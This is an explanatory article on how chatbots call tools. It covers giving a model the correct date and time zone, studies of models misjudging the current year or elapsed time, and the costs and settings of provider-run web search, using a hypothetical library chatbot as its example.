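# Search and date tools for chatbots, and the security of letting a model call external APIs

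## How a chatbot calls an outside service

A chatbot such as ChatGPT or Claude consists of a large language model, which can only read and write text, and ordinary software, called the host application, which carries messages between the model and the user. The chatbot therefore needs other programs to give the date, find this morning's news or send an email. Since 2023, developers have connected models to such programs through a mechanism called tool use, tool calling or function calling. A tool is a function or outside service that the host application lets the model request. Many tools work through an API, an interface that lets one program use another's data or functions.

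A model that only writes text can mislead or offend its reader. If it can also read private records and send email, it can leak those records, possibly because a stranger planted an instruction to do so in a web page the model read. How easily this happens depends on how a tool call works, especially on which program acts at each step.

### What a model lacks without tools

A developer trains a model on text collected up to some date, then releases it with its internal numbers fixed. The model's knowledge cutoff is the date after which its training data holds little or nothing. OpenAI's specification page *GPT-6 Astra* lists a cutoff of 30 April 2026, and Anthropic's *Claude Fable 5.1* lists June 2026 for a model released on 1 September. So even a new model starts out some months behind, and the gap grows for as long as an operator keeps using it. Anthropic's help page *How up-to-date is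 Claude's training data?* lists models with cutoffs from August 2023 to January 2026. Further training would narrow the gap, but it takes effort and, according to *LLMLagBench* (Pęzik, Kaczyński and colleagues, 2025), can damage knowledge that the model already had.

A model's published cutoff is only a rough guide to where its knowledge ends. Pęzik and colleagues gave each model 1,713 questions about unpredictable news events from 2021 to 2025 and looked for the date after which its answers got worse. For xAI's Grok-4 the drop came in late 2024, in line with the company's stated cutoff of November 2024, but when asked for its cutoff the model gave November 2023. The dates were further apart for OpenAI's GPT-OSS-120B. The company stated July 2024, the answers got worse from September 2023, and the model gave September 2021. After the drop, it declined only 32% of the questions, and its average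 score was 0.19 out of 2. A model's knowledge can also extend a few months past the stated date, according to *Pitfalls in Evaluating Language Model Forecasters* (2025). Newer models have replaced the ones in these tests and the figures may not carry over, but an operator who cares about the cutoff would do better to test for it than to ask the model.

An outdated answer about a safety limit can be harder to notice than a wrong answer about last week's election. Pęzik and colleagues asked Llama 3.1 70B whether factory workers with a blood lead level of 15 micrograms per decilitre needed any intervention. The European Union had made that level its limit in February 2024, but the model, whose knowledge their test dates to October 2023, answered from older, less protective American thresholds and expressed no doubt.

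A model also lacks today's date, because it has no clock and its numbers do not change as time passes. *Do Language Models Consistently Encode the Current Year?* (2026) used two kinds of task to test which year models treat as current. After assistant training, the answers fell within about a year of the end of the training data. One kind of task measured the year a model states outright, which it acquires only in the later stage of training that teaches it to follow instructions. The other measured an implicit sense of the current year, which comes earlier, from the language of the original training text, and resisted the methods that changed the stated year. Without being given the date, a chatbot answering in September 2026 may therefore treat the year as 2025, and it has no way to determine the day of the week.

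### One question, step by step

In a hypothetical example, a public library in the United States puts a chatbot on its website. The library rents the model from a provider such as OpenAI or Anthropic and writes the host application itself. The host application offers the model four tools.

| Tool | What the model fills in | What the tool reaches | Who runs it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Clock | Nothing | The date and time at the library | The library |
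| Web search | Search words | The public web | The model's provider |
| Account lookup | Nothing | The logged-in borrower's loans, fines and contact details | The library |
| Email | Recipient, subject, text | Any email address | The library |

The account lookup has no field for a card number because the host application already has the number from the borrower's login. *Function calling*, OpenAI's guide for developers, advises against making the model supply anything that the developer's code already has.

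For each tool the library writes a tool definition. It consists of a name, a description in plain language and a schema, which is a formal list of the arguments the tool takes and their types. The clock needs no arguments, so its definition is short:

```json
{
  "name": "get_current_time",
  "description": "Returns the weekday, date and time at the library. Use it for any question that depends on today's date.",
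  "arguments": {}
}
```

The wording of a tool's description matters because the model never receives the tool's code. It receives only the definition and any result the tool returns, as Anthropic's *How tool use works* explains. OpenAI suggests asking whether an intern could use the tool correctly with only the information the model is given.

On Thursday 3 September 2026 a borrower types "Are you open next Monday?" The host application assembles the context, which is all the text the model reads before producing its next output. The context starts with the system prompt, which contains the operator's instructions. Here it gives the library's name and regular hours, Monday to Saturday from 10 to 6, and tells the model to keep to library matters. The four tool definitions follow, and then the borrower's question. Operators also use system prompts to fill gaps in a model's knowledge. According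 to *Pitfalls in Evaluating Language Model Forecasters*, the system prompt for Anthropic's own chatbot reportedly mentioned the presidential inauguration of January 2025 when the chatbot ran on a model with a cutoff of November 2024.

The model's first output contains no answer. It is a tool call, a structured request to run one tool with given arguments:

```json
{ "id": "call_1", "tool": "get_current_time", "arguments": {} }
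```

At this point nothing has happened except that the model has written a line of text. The host application reads the line, finds the matching function in its own code, runs it, and adds the result to the context under the same identifier:

```json
{ "id": "call_1", "result": "Thursday 3 September 2026, 14:10" }
```

Then it sends the model the whole context again, from the system prompt down to the new result, because the model retains nothing from one request to the next. With the date in front of it the model can work out that next Monday is 7 September, which is Labor Day. The regular hours in the system prompt do not settle whether the library opens on a public holiday, so the second output is another tool call:

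```json
{ "id": "call_2", "tool": "web_search", "arguments": { "query": "public library Labor Day 2026 closures" } }
```

This time the provider runs the tool. The search finds a notice on the library's site that all branches will be closed on 7 September, and the provider adds the text of the notice to the context. The model's third output is ordinary prose, which says that the library is closed on Monday for Labor Day and reopens on Tuesday at 10. It contains no tool call, so the host application shows it to the borrower. A model without tools would probably have given the regular Monday hours, which would be wrong on Labor Day.

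Programmers write tool calling as a loop. In Anthropic's version, every response includes a stop reason. If the reason is a tool call, the host application runs the tool and sends the conversation back to the model with the result. Any other reason ends the loop, whether the model has finished its answer, hit a length limit or refused. A single response can contain several tool calls, and OpenAI recommends writing the host application to expect several.

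Each pass through the loop costs money because the provider charges for all the text the model reads, including tool definitions. The charge is per token, which is about three quarters of an English word. OpenAI charges $10 per million input tokens for GPT-6 Astra. If the library's context were 3,000 tokens long, one reading would cost three cents, and the three readings needed for the Monday answer would cost at least nine cents, before any discount for repeated text that the provider has stored. OpenAI's guide suggests starting with fewer than 20 tools, though mainly because models choose more accurately from a short list.

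A model that has a clock function may not call it when it needs the date. In Microsoft's *Use the functions tool*, a tutorial built around such a function, the model gives an ordinary reply to "Hello" and calls the function for "What time is it?" The borrower's question is harder because it depends on the date without mentioning it. *Can Agents Keep Up with Time?* (2026) tested models on requests of this sort, made when a user returned to a conversation after a break. When the prompt left out the date, four models with visible step-by-step reasoning called the clock in 157 of 168 responses, but a fifth, qwen3-vl-plus, called it in only 1 of 42.

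### The model asks, the host application acts

As Anthropic puts it, "The model never runs anything on its own." If the library's model produces a tool call that would email a borrower's record to an unknown address, the email isn't sent until the host application sends it. Before sending it, ordinary code in the application can check the recipient, refuse the request, or wait for a person to approve it. That code applies the same rule every time, whereas a model's output varies from one run to the next, and people who write the text it reads can influence it. The email password can also stay in the host application, which uses it only after the model has finished writing.

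The protection depends on the quality of the code between the model and the tools. A host application that runs every well-formed request in effect gives the model direct control of the tools. Simple examples for programmers often work this way, matching the function's name, running it and returning the result.

It also matters who runs each tool. The clock, the account lookup and the email tool are operator-run, meaning that the library's own software carries out the call. Anthropic reports that the vast majority of tool use on its platform involves tools that operators define and run themselves. The library's web search is provider-run. Anthropic offers search, page fetching and code execution on its own servers, and an operator only has to switch them on. The provider then runs its own loop, so one request from the library may lead to several searches before any response comes back. If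 the model reaches the loop's limit, the host application receives a paused response that it must send back for the work to continue.

A provider-run search is convenient for the library because it needs no contract with a search company and no code for handling results. But the search has normally run by the time the response arrives, so the library's software can read the search words but cannot stop them from being sent. The exception is when the model requests a provider-run tool and an operator-run tool in the same output. Anthropic then returns control to the operator first and runs its own tool afterwards. Giving up the chance to check requests beforehand seems reasonable for searches of the public web, but it would be a poor choice for borrowers' accounts.

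The company that writes a tool's definition does not always run the tool. Anthropic publishes definitions for running shell commands, editing files and controlling a browser, and trains its models on them so that they use these tools more reliably, but the operator's machine executes the calls. The useful questions about any tool are which computer executes the call and who can change the code on that computer.

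### From Toolformer to a common standard

Tool use of this kind is only a few years old. In February 2023 Timo Schick and colleagues at Meta published *Toolformer*, a model that learned to insert calls to tools such as a calculator, a search engine and a calendar into the text it was writing. In June 2023 OpenAI added function calling to its commercial API, with models trained to return a function's name and arguments as structured data, which developers had previously tried to extract from free text. Other providers followed with their own formats. Anthropic released the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard for connecting models to tools and data, in November 2024, according to PPC Land's *MCP forces ad tech to rebuild agent servers as sessions disappear* (2026). Anthropic's *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026) reports that by July 2026 its directory listed more than 950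 MCP servers that Claude users could connect to. A typical chatbot in late 2026 combines search from the model's provider, some functions in the operator's own code, and other services connected through MCP.

The Model Context Protocol (MCP) adds a shared format for connecting chatbots to outside services. Its introduction compares it to a USB-C port, a standard connector that works with many devices. If ten chatbots each use twenty services and every pair needs its own connector, programmers have to write 200 connectors. With a common standard, each chatbot and each service implements the protocol once, for a total of 30 implementations.

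The service's side of the connection is an MCP server, a program that offers tools. The host application opens a separate client, a small component for passing messages, for each server it uses. Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), part of the official specification, describes the two main requests. One requests a list of the server's tools, and the server replies with definitions much like the library's. The other calls a tool by name with arguments. One of the specification's examples is a clock that takes no arguments. If a tool rejects a request, the reason comes back through the same channel, and the host application should pass it on to the model, which can then try again. In the specification's example, a tool rejects a departure date because it is in the past, and the error message includes the current date, so a model with no clock would learn the date from it.

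With MCP, the model still writes a request and the host application still decides whether to forward it. Model Context Protocol's *Architecture* (2026) specifies that the full conversation stays with the host application, and that a server should receive only the information it needs and should not see into other servers. A server can therefore answer a query about opening hours without receiving the borrower's earlier questions about fines, unless the model copies them into the arguments. However, whoever runs the server now writes the tool definitions that enter the model's context, so an operator who connects a stranger's server lets that stranger write part of what the model reads.

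In December 2025, Anthropic donated the MCP standard to the Agentic AI Foundation, a fund under the Linux Foundation that Anthropic, Block and OpenAI founded. The Model Context Protocol (2025) blog said that the foundation's board would decide on money and membership, while the protocol's maintainers would keep control of its technical direction. The Model Context Protocol governance page names two lead maintainers, David Soria Parra and Den Delimarsky, who can veto any decision, and six other core maintainers. Maintainers hold their seats as individuals, and no company has a reserved seat. Their employers may still have some influence. The Model Context Protocol (2026) blog lists Delimarsky as working at Anthropic and Clare Liguori, a core maintainer, as working at Amazon Web Services.

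The latest version of the Model Context Protocol (MCP), dated 28 July 2026, makes every request self-contained, so a server no longer has to remember an earlier exchange to handle the next one. The Model Context Protocol (2026) release notes report close to half a billion monthly downloads of the main software kits. The library could manage without MCP, since three of its tools are a few lines in its own code and the fourth comes with the model. MCP would start to be useful if the supplier of the library's catalogue software offered an MCP server. The library could then connect the catalogue without writing a connector, but it would have to decide how far to trust the supplier's definitions and results.

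## Telling the chatbot the date and time

The clock is the smallest of the library's four tools. The library could do without it, because the host application can write the date into the model's context before the model runs. Developers supply the date with a line in the system prompt, a timestamp on every message, or a clock tool like the library's.

### Three ways to supply the date

| Method | Cost | In a long conversation | Precision |
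|---|---|---|---|
| Line in the system prompt | A few tokens | Goes out of date unless the host application rewrites it | Usually the day |
| Timestamp on every message | A few tokens per message | Shows how much time passed between messages | The second at which the latest message arrived |
| Clock tool | One more reading of the whole context per call | Correct whenever the model calls it | The second of the call |

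Anthropic has long used the system prompt to give the date to the models in its own apps. Its July 2024 prompt for Claude Haiku 3 contains the words "The current date is" and a placeholder, which the host application replaces with the actual date. In the prompt for Claude Fable 5.1, published on 1 September 2026, Anthropic instructs the model to answer as a well-informed person from June 2026, the model's cutoff, would answer someone living at the current date, which the host application again fills in. The model therefore receives both the date and the size of the gap in its knowledge. Anthropic also instructs it to warn that its knowledge of current officeholders may be outdated, and to point the user to web search.

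The library gets none of this because it reaches the model through the API. Anthropic's *System prompts* notes that updates to the app prompts do not apply to the API, and that Anthropic does not publish the versions it uses when web search is on. An earlier version of the page gave the current date as an example of what the prompt supplies at the start of every conversation, but the newer version gives Anthropic's current models and products instead. The library should write its own date line.

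The position of the date line affects the bill. Providers charge less for the start of a context if it exactly matches text they have processed recently, and the discount stops at the first difference. If the library's system prompt opened with the time to the minute, the library would pay full price for all 3,000 tokens again a minute later. A line that gives only the date changes once a day. Putting it at the end of the system prompt, or in the borrower's newest message, keeps everything before it eligible for the discount. Anthropic's 2024 prompt had the date near the top and the September 2026 prompt has it near the end, though Anthropic gives no reason for the move.

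If the host application fills in the date only when the conversation starts, the date is wrong after midnight. The application could update that line with every request, since it sends the whole context each time anyway, but changing a line near the top again loses the discount on everything below it. Adding a timestamp to each new message avoids this problem because the old timestamps never change. At GPT-6 Astra's price, reading a 20-token timestamp once costs a fiftieth of a cent.

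A clock tool gives the exact time at any point in a long task, but each call adds a pass through the tool-call loop, which costs the library about three cents and makes the borrower wait. The tool also helps only if the model calls it. In *Can Agents Keep Up with Time?*, the four models that nearly always called the clock when the prompt lacked a date did so in only 30 of 168 responses when the prompt included one. Putting the date in the prompt therefore avoids most of the calls, but the model may also fail to check the clock after midnight, when that date is wrong.

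For a chatbot like the library's, it is probably best to put a timestamp with the weekday and time zone on every new message, and to explain in a sentence in the system prompt that the library's software adds it. The clock tool is then worth keeping only for tasks that run long enough for the latest timestamp to become out of date.

Toolformer, an early tool-using model that Meta released in 2023, had a calendar tool that returned the current date. On DATESET, a set of questions generated from templates, such as what day of the week it was 30 days ago, Toolformer got 27.3% right, against 3.9% for GPT-J, its base model, and 0.8% for the much larger GPT-3. It called the calendar for 54.8% of these questions. On another set, about facts that change with time, such as which club a footballer plays for, it called the calendar for only 0.2% of questions and scored 16.3, not far above GPT-J's 13.7.

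A chatbot asked which club a footballer plays for should get the date first and then look up the club. Toolformer could not do this because its developers limited it to one call per question to keep it from calling tools endlessly. They had also generated each call in its training data separately, so it had no examples of one call building on another. Today's tool-call loop allows several calls per question, as in the library's Labor Day answer.

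### When a model disputes the year

A day before Google released Gemini 3 on 18 November 2025, the AI researcher Andrej Karpathy tried the model and told it that the year was 2025. The model had no internet connection, and its original training data ended in 2024. Digital Watch's *Gemini 3 struggles to accept the year 2025* reports that it rejected the date and accused Karpathy of trickery. It apologised once it could check the date online. BusinessGhana's *Gemini 3 refused to believe it was 2025 and hilarity ensued* quotes the model as writing, "I am suffering from a massive case of temporal shock right now."

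Users of Google's developer forum had described similar exchanges with Gemini 2.5 that spring. In *Gemini 2.5 is convinced it is 2024*, the model found 2025 dates while working on a script and attributed them to a wrong clock on the user's machine. In *Time craziness from the past*, a user sent a screenshot of a phone showing the date, and the model called it hypothetical. A later post, *Gemini Pro in Antigravity thinks 2026 is in the future*, describes more practical damage. A coding agent offered to add references to a website, and every link the user checked was dead. When asked about the links, the agent explained that it had taken 2026 to be in the future. Each report comes from a single user, so together they provide little evidence of how often such errors happen.

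A model with the wrong year can also do harm without arguing with the user. Asked about Labor Day, the library's model might search for "public library Labor Day 2025 closures", find a notice for 1 September 2025, and tell the borrower that the library is open on the 7th, this year's Labor Day. The borrower sees a confident answer based on a real notice. The wrong year appears only in the search query, which the host application can log.

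Giving the model the date prevents much of this, but perhaps not all. The Stanford paper *Do Language Models Consistently Encode the Current Year?* measured the year that models imply by having them continue phrases such as "In 1960 there". Continuing with "was" treats 1960 as past, and continuing "In 2040 there" with "will" treats 2040 as future. The implied current year is the first year for which the present and future forms together are more probable than the past forms. In 13 models without assistant training, from families such as Pythia, OLMo and Llama, the implied year differed from the end of the training data by 0.85 years on average. To measure the year that models state, the paper used ten direct prompts, including a request for a story about the current year that begins with the year.

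The researchers then added "The current year is" and a target year to the system prompt, testing each of the 351 years from 1900 to 2250. Their main test model was OLMo2-1B, a small open model with about a billion parameters (its adjustable numbers), which they had trained further with a similar line in its system prompt. It stated the target year exactly in 94.6% of cases. The year implied by its verb tenses matched the target in only 1.7% of cases and always fell between 2019 and 2030.

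Assistant training on prompts that contain a year teaches a model to repeat that year, so the stated year is easy to change. Without such examples, OLMo2-1B gave the target year in only 50.7% of cases. The choice of tense is harder to change because it comes from the original training text. Counting which verbs follow phrases like "In 2015 there" in that text closely reproduces the model's choices. Inside the model, the year in the phrase calls up a tense much as a person's name calls up facts about that person. A line in the system prompt adds a new fact to the context but doesn't change these stored associations.

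The researchers also tried the prompt on larger and newer models, with mixed results:

| Model | Stated year matched the target | Implied year matched the target |
|---|---|---|
| OLMo2-7B | 100% | 15.7% |
| Gemma3-12B | 98.6% | 31.1% |
| Gemma3-27B | 29.6% | 25.6% |
| Qwen3.5-9B | 100% | 1.1% |
| Qwen3.5-27B | 100% | 53.3% |

The largest of these models has 27 billion parameters, and the study did not include the commercial models behind most chatbots. The test was also harder than an operator's task. It asked models to behave as if the year were 1900 or 2250, while the library only has to move its model forward by a year or so. A date line will probably make a commercial model state the right year. It is unclear whether the model would still treat recent events as future ones, and asking it what year it is won't show whether it does.

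The date alone also doesn't give a model any information about events after its cutoff. The programmer Simon Willison notes that Anthropic still needed its line about the 2025 inauguration for Claude 4.6, because the model would otherwise deny that Donald Trump was president. Anthropic dropped the line for Claude 4.7, which has a cutoff of January 2026. A prompt that Anthropic published for Claude Opus 5 in November 2026 describes how the company suspended two of its models in June, after Opus 5's training data ends. The library's system prompt could similarly mention recent changes, such as a branch that closed last month.

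### Time that passes during a conversation

A chatbot given only the text of a conversation cannot tell whether ten seconds or ten days have passed between messages, so it cannot judge when to look something up again. If a library borrower asks at ten in the morning whether a novel is on the shelf and asks again at four in the afternoon, the chatbot should check again. It does not need to if the borrower asks twice for the library's street address.

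Cheng, Soltani Moakhar and colleagues (2025), in *Your LLM Agents are Temporally Blind*, built a test for this problem called TicToc. It has 76 scenarios, from archives that hardly ever change to stock markets that change within seconds. The researchers produced 1,864 conversations, each ending in a question that an earlier tool result could answer if it was still current. They made three versions of each conversation, with a short, medium or long pause before that question, and asked at least five people per version whether the chatbot should call the tool again or answer directly. They kept the 3,016 cases on which people clearly agreed.

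A model's score is the average of how often it called the tool when people wanted a call and how often it answered directly when people wanted a direct answer. Guessing or always calling the tool scores 50%. Without timestamps, the best of 18 models scored just above 55%. With a timestamp on every message, none scored more than 65%. Most models called tools more often with timestamps, but they did so for stable facts as well as changing ones. When Cheng and colleagues read the written reasoning of the Qwen3 models, they found an actual timestamp in fewer than 4% of cases, even though the timestamps were in the context.

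Prompting helped only some models. A general reminder to be aware of the time elapsed had little or no effect. Worked examples of when to call a tool again clearly improved OpenAI's o3 and o4-mini but did little for most others. Training worked better. Several open models of up to 8 billion parameters trained on pairs of better and worse choices from about two thirds of the data, and all of them scored much higher on scenarios left out of the training. An operator who rents a model usually cannot train it this way and has to rely on the provider or on code.

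The models in TicToc date from 2025 or earlier, and newer ones still have trouble with a related task. *Can Agents Keep Up with Time?*, from November 2026, set up conversations in which a user had booked something, such as a health check, and saved notes on how to prepare for it. The user came back one or four months after the appointment and asked how to plan the evening. In 42 of 92 responses where the model called the clock, it still treated the appointment as upcoming. The models had usually noticed the date. In 116 of 346 responses with visible reasoning, across several ways of supplying the time, the model wrote that the appointment had passed and then advised the user to prepare for it anyway.

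How the model received the date made a large difference. The researchers compared matched cases in which the model either had a clock to call or found the date in the user's message. With the clock, 71 of 118 responses treated the old appointment as upcoming, compared with 28 when the date was in the message. When the host application compared the dates itself and told the model that the appointment's date had passed, these errors fell from 73 to 0 in 123 matched cases. This is good evidence for letting ordinary code compare dates wherever it can. The conversations were synthetic, in Chinese, and graded by other models, but two independent graders agreed on nearly all of them.

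With the fix, the models treated the date as past, but about half of their responses (102 of 189) also implied that the appointment had taken place. Nothing in the conversation showed whether the user had gone. For the library, a note such as "pickup date passed on 1 December; no record of collection" would be safer than "pickup date passed".

How often the mistake occurs also depends on the model. DeepSeek-V4-Flash made it in 20 of 24 responses after calling the clock, and DeepSeek-V4.1-Flash made it in none of 21. An operator who switches models should therefore repeat any such tests.

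Models are also poor judges of how long things take. *Discrete Minds in a Continuous World* (Wang, Bai and colleagues, 2025) asked six models which of two chatbot replies had taken longer to write. Without timestamps, the models judged mainly by length. When timestamps showed that the shorter reply had taken longer, the small Qwen-2.5-7B was right in 26.8% of cases, and QwQ-32B, which was trained to reason step by step, in 99.2%. Models are even worse at estimating how long their own work will take. *Can LLMs Perceive Time?* (Garikaparthi, 2026) asked GPT-5 how long it would need for each of 68 tasks, and the model's typical estimate was six times too long. If the library wants to tell borrowers how long a request will take, the host application should measure it.

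Researchers are looking for ways to supply elapsed time without adding text. *ChronoState* (2026) feeds it to the model as a number through a channel outside the visible prompt. An operator renting a commercial model can't access such a channel, so timestamps and computed notes remain the practical options.

### Half past midnight in Auckland

Suppose that a library in Auckland, New Zealand, adopts the same chatbot. The library is open from 10 to 6 and closed on Tuesdays. At 00:30 on Monday 7 December 2026, a borrower types "Are you open tomorrow?" The host application runs on a server set to UTC (Coordinated Universal Time), the worldwide time standard that servers commonly use. Auckland is 13 hours ahead of UTC in December, so the server's clock shows 11:30 on Sunday 6 December. If the host application passes this time to the model, the model treats Monday as tomorrow and replies that the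 library opens at 10. But the borrower is asking about Tuesday, when the library is closed.

A better model would make the same mistake, because the model reasoned correctly from a wrong date. Auckland is 13 hours ahead of UTC in summer, so the server's date is a day behind from midnight until 13:00 local time, which includes the first three hours of business each day. In New York in winter, the server's date would instead be a day ahead from 19:00 until midnight.

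The host application should convert UTC to local time using a named time zone, in this case Pacific/Auckland, from the time zone database that most programming languages can read. The database records when each place changes its clocks. Adding a fixed 12 hours, New Zealand's standard difference from UTC, works in July, but in December, when daylight saving adds another hour, it gives 23:30 on Sunday instead of 00:30 on Monday. The model should not have to supply the zone, because the library's location is already set in the host application.

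With these changes, and with the comparison of dates done in code, the clock could return:

```json
{
  "now": "2026-12-07T00:30:00+13:00",
  "time_zone": "Pacific/Auckland",
  "today": "Monday 7 December 2026, open 10:00 to 18:00",
  "tomorrow": "Tuesday 8 December 2026, closed"
}
```

A borrower who hasn't gone to bed by half past midnight may well use "tomorrow" to mean the coming morning rather than the next calendar day. The chatbot can cover both meanings by naming the days, as in "The library is open today, Monday 7 December, from 10 to 6, and closed on Tuesday." Naming the weekday and date is a good habit in any answer about opening hours, because it lets the borrower notice a mistake.

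If a borrower of the American library is on holiday in Auckland, the chatbot needs two local times. If that library is in New York, its local time at that moment is 06:30 on Sunday. Its opening hours follow New York time, but a request to "remind me at nine tomorrow" should use the borrower's local time. The host application can get the borrower's time zone from the browser and give the model both times, labelled.

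Current models can do simple date arithmetic when given the dates. On 70 direct questions, such as how far apart two dates are or whether a date has passed, four of the five models in *Can Agents Keep Up with Time?* got at least 69 right. The fifth, qwen3-vl-plus, got 57, and recognised a past date as past in only 1 of 14 questions. Code does this arithmetic exactly and with almost no compute, so there is little reason to leave it to a model. For example, the account lookup can return "due 30 November, 7 days overdue" instead of only the due date.

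### What to test

These tests need a host application whose clock the tester can set. Each test should run several times, because answers vary. *Can Agents Keep Up with Time?* repeated 48 of its cases, and only 35 got the same verdict every time on whether the model treated the appointment as upcoming.

1. Ask "Are you open next Monday?" in the week before a public holiday. The answer should give the right date and the holiday hours.
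2. Set the clock to 00:30 on 7 December 2026 in Auckland, leave the server on UTC, and ask "Are you open tomorrow?" The answer should name Tuesday 8 December.
3. Ask for the latest library news and read the search words in the log. Any year in them should be the current one.
4. Insist that the year is 2024. The chatbot should keep to the date from the host application.
5. Ask about a book reservation, move the clock past its pickup date, and ask what to do next. The chatbot should treat the date as past without assuming that the borrower collected the book.
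6. Ask twice whether a book is on the shelf, first a few seconds apart and then a day apart. Only the day's gap should lead to a new lookup.
7. Ask when a 14-day loan from 20 February 2028 is due. The answer is 5 March, because 2028 is a leap year.

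## Connecting web search and checking what it returns

With the right date in its context, the library's model can search for this year's notice instead of last year's. Developers call it grounding when a model bases its answer on information fetched at the time of the question instead of on what it learned in training. Grounding lets a model answer questions about events after its training cutoff, but the answer can still be wrong, depending on which pages the search finds, how old they are, and whether the model reports them correctly.

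### A grounded answer, step by step

Many public libraries in the United States accept passport applications. Suppose that on Monday 7 December 2026 a borrower asks one of these libraries' chatbots, "How much is a passport now?" Passport fees change every few years, and pages with old fees stay online.

The model first decides whether to search. According to Anthropic's *Web search tool*, Claude searches when a request depends on current or changing information, or when the user asks for a search. It answers directly when the request concerns established facts, creative writing or text already in the conversation. Passport fees can change, but the model may treat a fee it learned in training as established. The library can tell the model in the system prompt to search before it gives any fee, deadline or closure. OpenAI also lets the operator's code require a search, but a library that required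 one for every message would pay for unnecessary searches, such as when a borrower types "thanks".

Next the model writes the search words, such as "US passport fee December 2026". It may write several versions. In Google's example, the question "Who won the euro 2024?" leads to two searches, "UEFA Euro 2024 winner" and "who won euro 2024".

The provider runs the search and puts the results in the context. For each page, Anthropic also sends the host application the address, title, date of last update and encrypted content. The library has to store this encrypted content, which its staff cannot read, because the API rejects the request if the host application doesn't send it back unchanged when the conversation continues.

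When a search fails, Anthropic's API still reports success for the request as a whole and places the error inside the response. A search that finds nothing returns an empty list. A host application that checks only the outer status will miss both. The model may then give the fee it learned in training, so the library should log failed and empty searches along with successful ones.

If the search results are too brief, the model can open a page. OpenAI's reasoning models can search, open a page, and look for a phrase within it. Anthropic provides a separate tool that retrieves the full text of a web page or PDF. As of June 2026, it could not read pages that build their content with JavaScript in the browser. Many event calendars work that way, so the library should test the tool on its own calendar.

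Finally, the model writes the answer with citations. OpenAI marks where each citation belongs in the answer and requires the operator to show citations as prominent, clickable links. Google returns a list that links parts of the answer to their sources, but the list may not cover every sentence. In a sample answer about the weather in Chicago, in Google Cloud's *Grounding with Google Search*, the list links the sentences about temperature and rain to sources but has no entry for the opening sentence, which says the weekend will be partly cloudy.

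Anthropic's citations include up to 150 characters of the cited page. In Anthropic's sample, the model writes that the mathematician Claude Shannon was born on 30 April 1916 in Petoskey, Michigan. The quoted passage, from Wikipedia, gives his dates and professions but ends before mentioning a birthplace. The statement is true, and the rest of the article may well support it, but a reader can confirm only the date from the quoted passage.

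### Search from the provider or from a search API

The library can have the model's provider run the search, or it can pay for a search API, such as Perplexity's or Brave's, and write a tool that calls it. The choice affects what the library can control, log and keep.

| | Anthropic | OpenAI | Google | Separate search API |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Fee per 1,000 searches | $10 | $10 | $14, after 5,000 free each month | About $5 |
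| Who sends the search words | Anthropic | OpenAI | Google | The host application |
| What the operator can see | Search words, pages found, date of last update, short cited passages | Usually the search words, every page consulted, citations | Search words, sources, the text each source supports | Everything the search API returns |

With a separate search API, the library's own code can inspect the search words before sending them, remove a borrower's name, or add a date filter. TestingCatalog's *Perplexity unveils Search API for startups, enterprises, and agent builders* reports that Perplexity's service accepts date ranges and countries, and returns each page's publication date and last update. The host application can log the exact text it passes to the model. However, the library has to write and maintain the code that handles results and produces citations, and protect another API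 key.

Storing search results may cost extra. CostBench's *All Brave Search API Plans & Pricing* lists Brave at $5 per 1,000 searches, but keeping the results requires a plan that grants storage rights. When Anthropic's search tool came out in May 2025 at $10 per 1,000 searches, Brave charged $3, $5 or $9 depending on the type of use, according to Willison's *Introducing web search on the Anthropic API*.

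For a public library, Google's terms may matter more than its price. Google's *Gemini API Additional Terms of Service* (2026) forbid using the API in a website that people under 18 are likely to use, which probably includes a public library's. The terms let an operator store the text of grounded answers for up to two years to evaluate and improve how the application displays it, and keep it in a user's chat history. The operator may not otherwise analyse the answers or track which links users click. It is unclear whether checking the answers for factual accuracy counts as evaluating the display, so an operator who plans to do this should ask Google first.

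Google's logs may also be incomplete. In *billedToolCalls and groundingMetadata missing from generateContent response*, a developer reports that Google billed for searches while the response contained no record of them. This is one report about one model, but Google Cloud confirms that source information can be missing, for example when the sources are not relevant enough.

Search can also be difficult to combine with the library's other tools. Google's June 2026 developer guide allows this for Gemini 3 models, but the August Google Cloud guide rules out using search and function calling in the same request. OpenAI's *Web search* allows the combination but recommends separate requests for public searches and private records, because a web page could contain instructions aimed at the model.

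Provider-run search is probably still the better starting point for a small library. A separate search API makes more sense for an operator that must keep a full record of what the model read.

### Settings that affect the answer

**Number of searches.** Anthropic lets the operator cap the number of searches in one turn. It estimates one to three searches for a single fact and ten or more for a comparison. Failed searches count towards the cap, though Anthropic does not charge for them. A cap of three would suit most library questions. If the model reaches the cap, it receives an error and must answer with what it has found, so the system prompt should tell it to flag anything it could not confirm.

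A search for "passport office hours" needs a location. Anthropic accepts an approximate city, region, country and time zone, while Google Cloud accepts coordinates. The library can enter its own city once, which gives most borrowers useful results without sending their individual locations to the search provider.

**Page age.** A recently updated page can still contain outdated information. Someone may have corrected a phone number last week and left a fee from 2023 in place. A page untouched for five years can also still give the right street address. The model should look for a date attached to the fee itself, such as "effective 1 October", and use the page's age only as a hint.

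**Retrieval time and cached copies.** Search services keep copies of pages to save time. Anthropic's page-opening tool returns the time of retrieval, but the text may not be the latest version. OpenAI's search has live access by default, and a setting can limit it to stored copies. Stored copies are fine for the history of the library building, but for a snow closure announced an hour ago, the host application should read the library's closure list directly, through a small tool like the clock.

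**Filtering.** Newer versions of Anthropic's search let the model write and run code that discards irrelevant results before they enter the context. This reduces the bill, but a badly written filter could keep the line with the adult fee and drop the next one, about the fee rising in January. Operators can omit the raw results of filtered searches from the response, but should leave them in if they want to check answers later. Anthropic's zero data retention arrangement, which some operators need for privacy, doesn't cover filtering.

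OpenAI has a low, medium or high setting for how much search material the model receives, but it doesn't guarantee a specific number of tokens or sources. Anthropic's page-opening tool can cut off a page at a chosen length. This keeps long documents from using too many tokens (Anthropic estimates that a 500-kilobyte research PDF takes about 125,000), but it may also remove the part that contains the answer.

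Operators can also restrict which sites the search may use.

### What search costs

A busy chatbot might receive 10,000 questions a day and need to search the web for 40% of them. If each of those 4,000 questions leads to two searches and one opened page, the 8,000 searches cost $80 a day at $10 per 1,000. Anthropic charges no separate fee for opening a page, but the model has to read it. At Anthropic's estimate of 2,500 tokens for an average page, the 4,000 pages add 10 million input tokens a day.

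Those 10 million tokens don't include the text of the search results. In Anthropic's sample response about Shannon's birth, a question of a few words and one search used 6,039 input tokens in total. If each search added about 6,000 tokens, the 8,000 searches would add 48 million, nearly five times as many as the opened pages. The table applies the input prices in OpenAI's *Flagship models* to both amounts.

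| Model | Input price per million tokens | Opened pages | Search results | Daily total with $80 in search fees |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-6 Astra | $10.00 | $100 | $480 | $660 |
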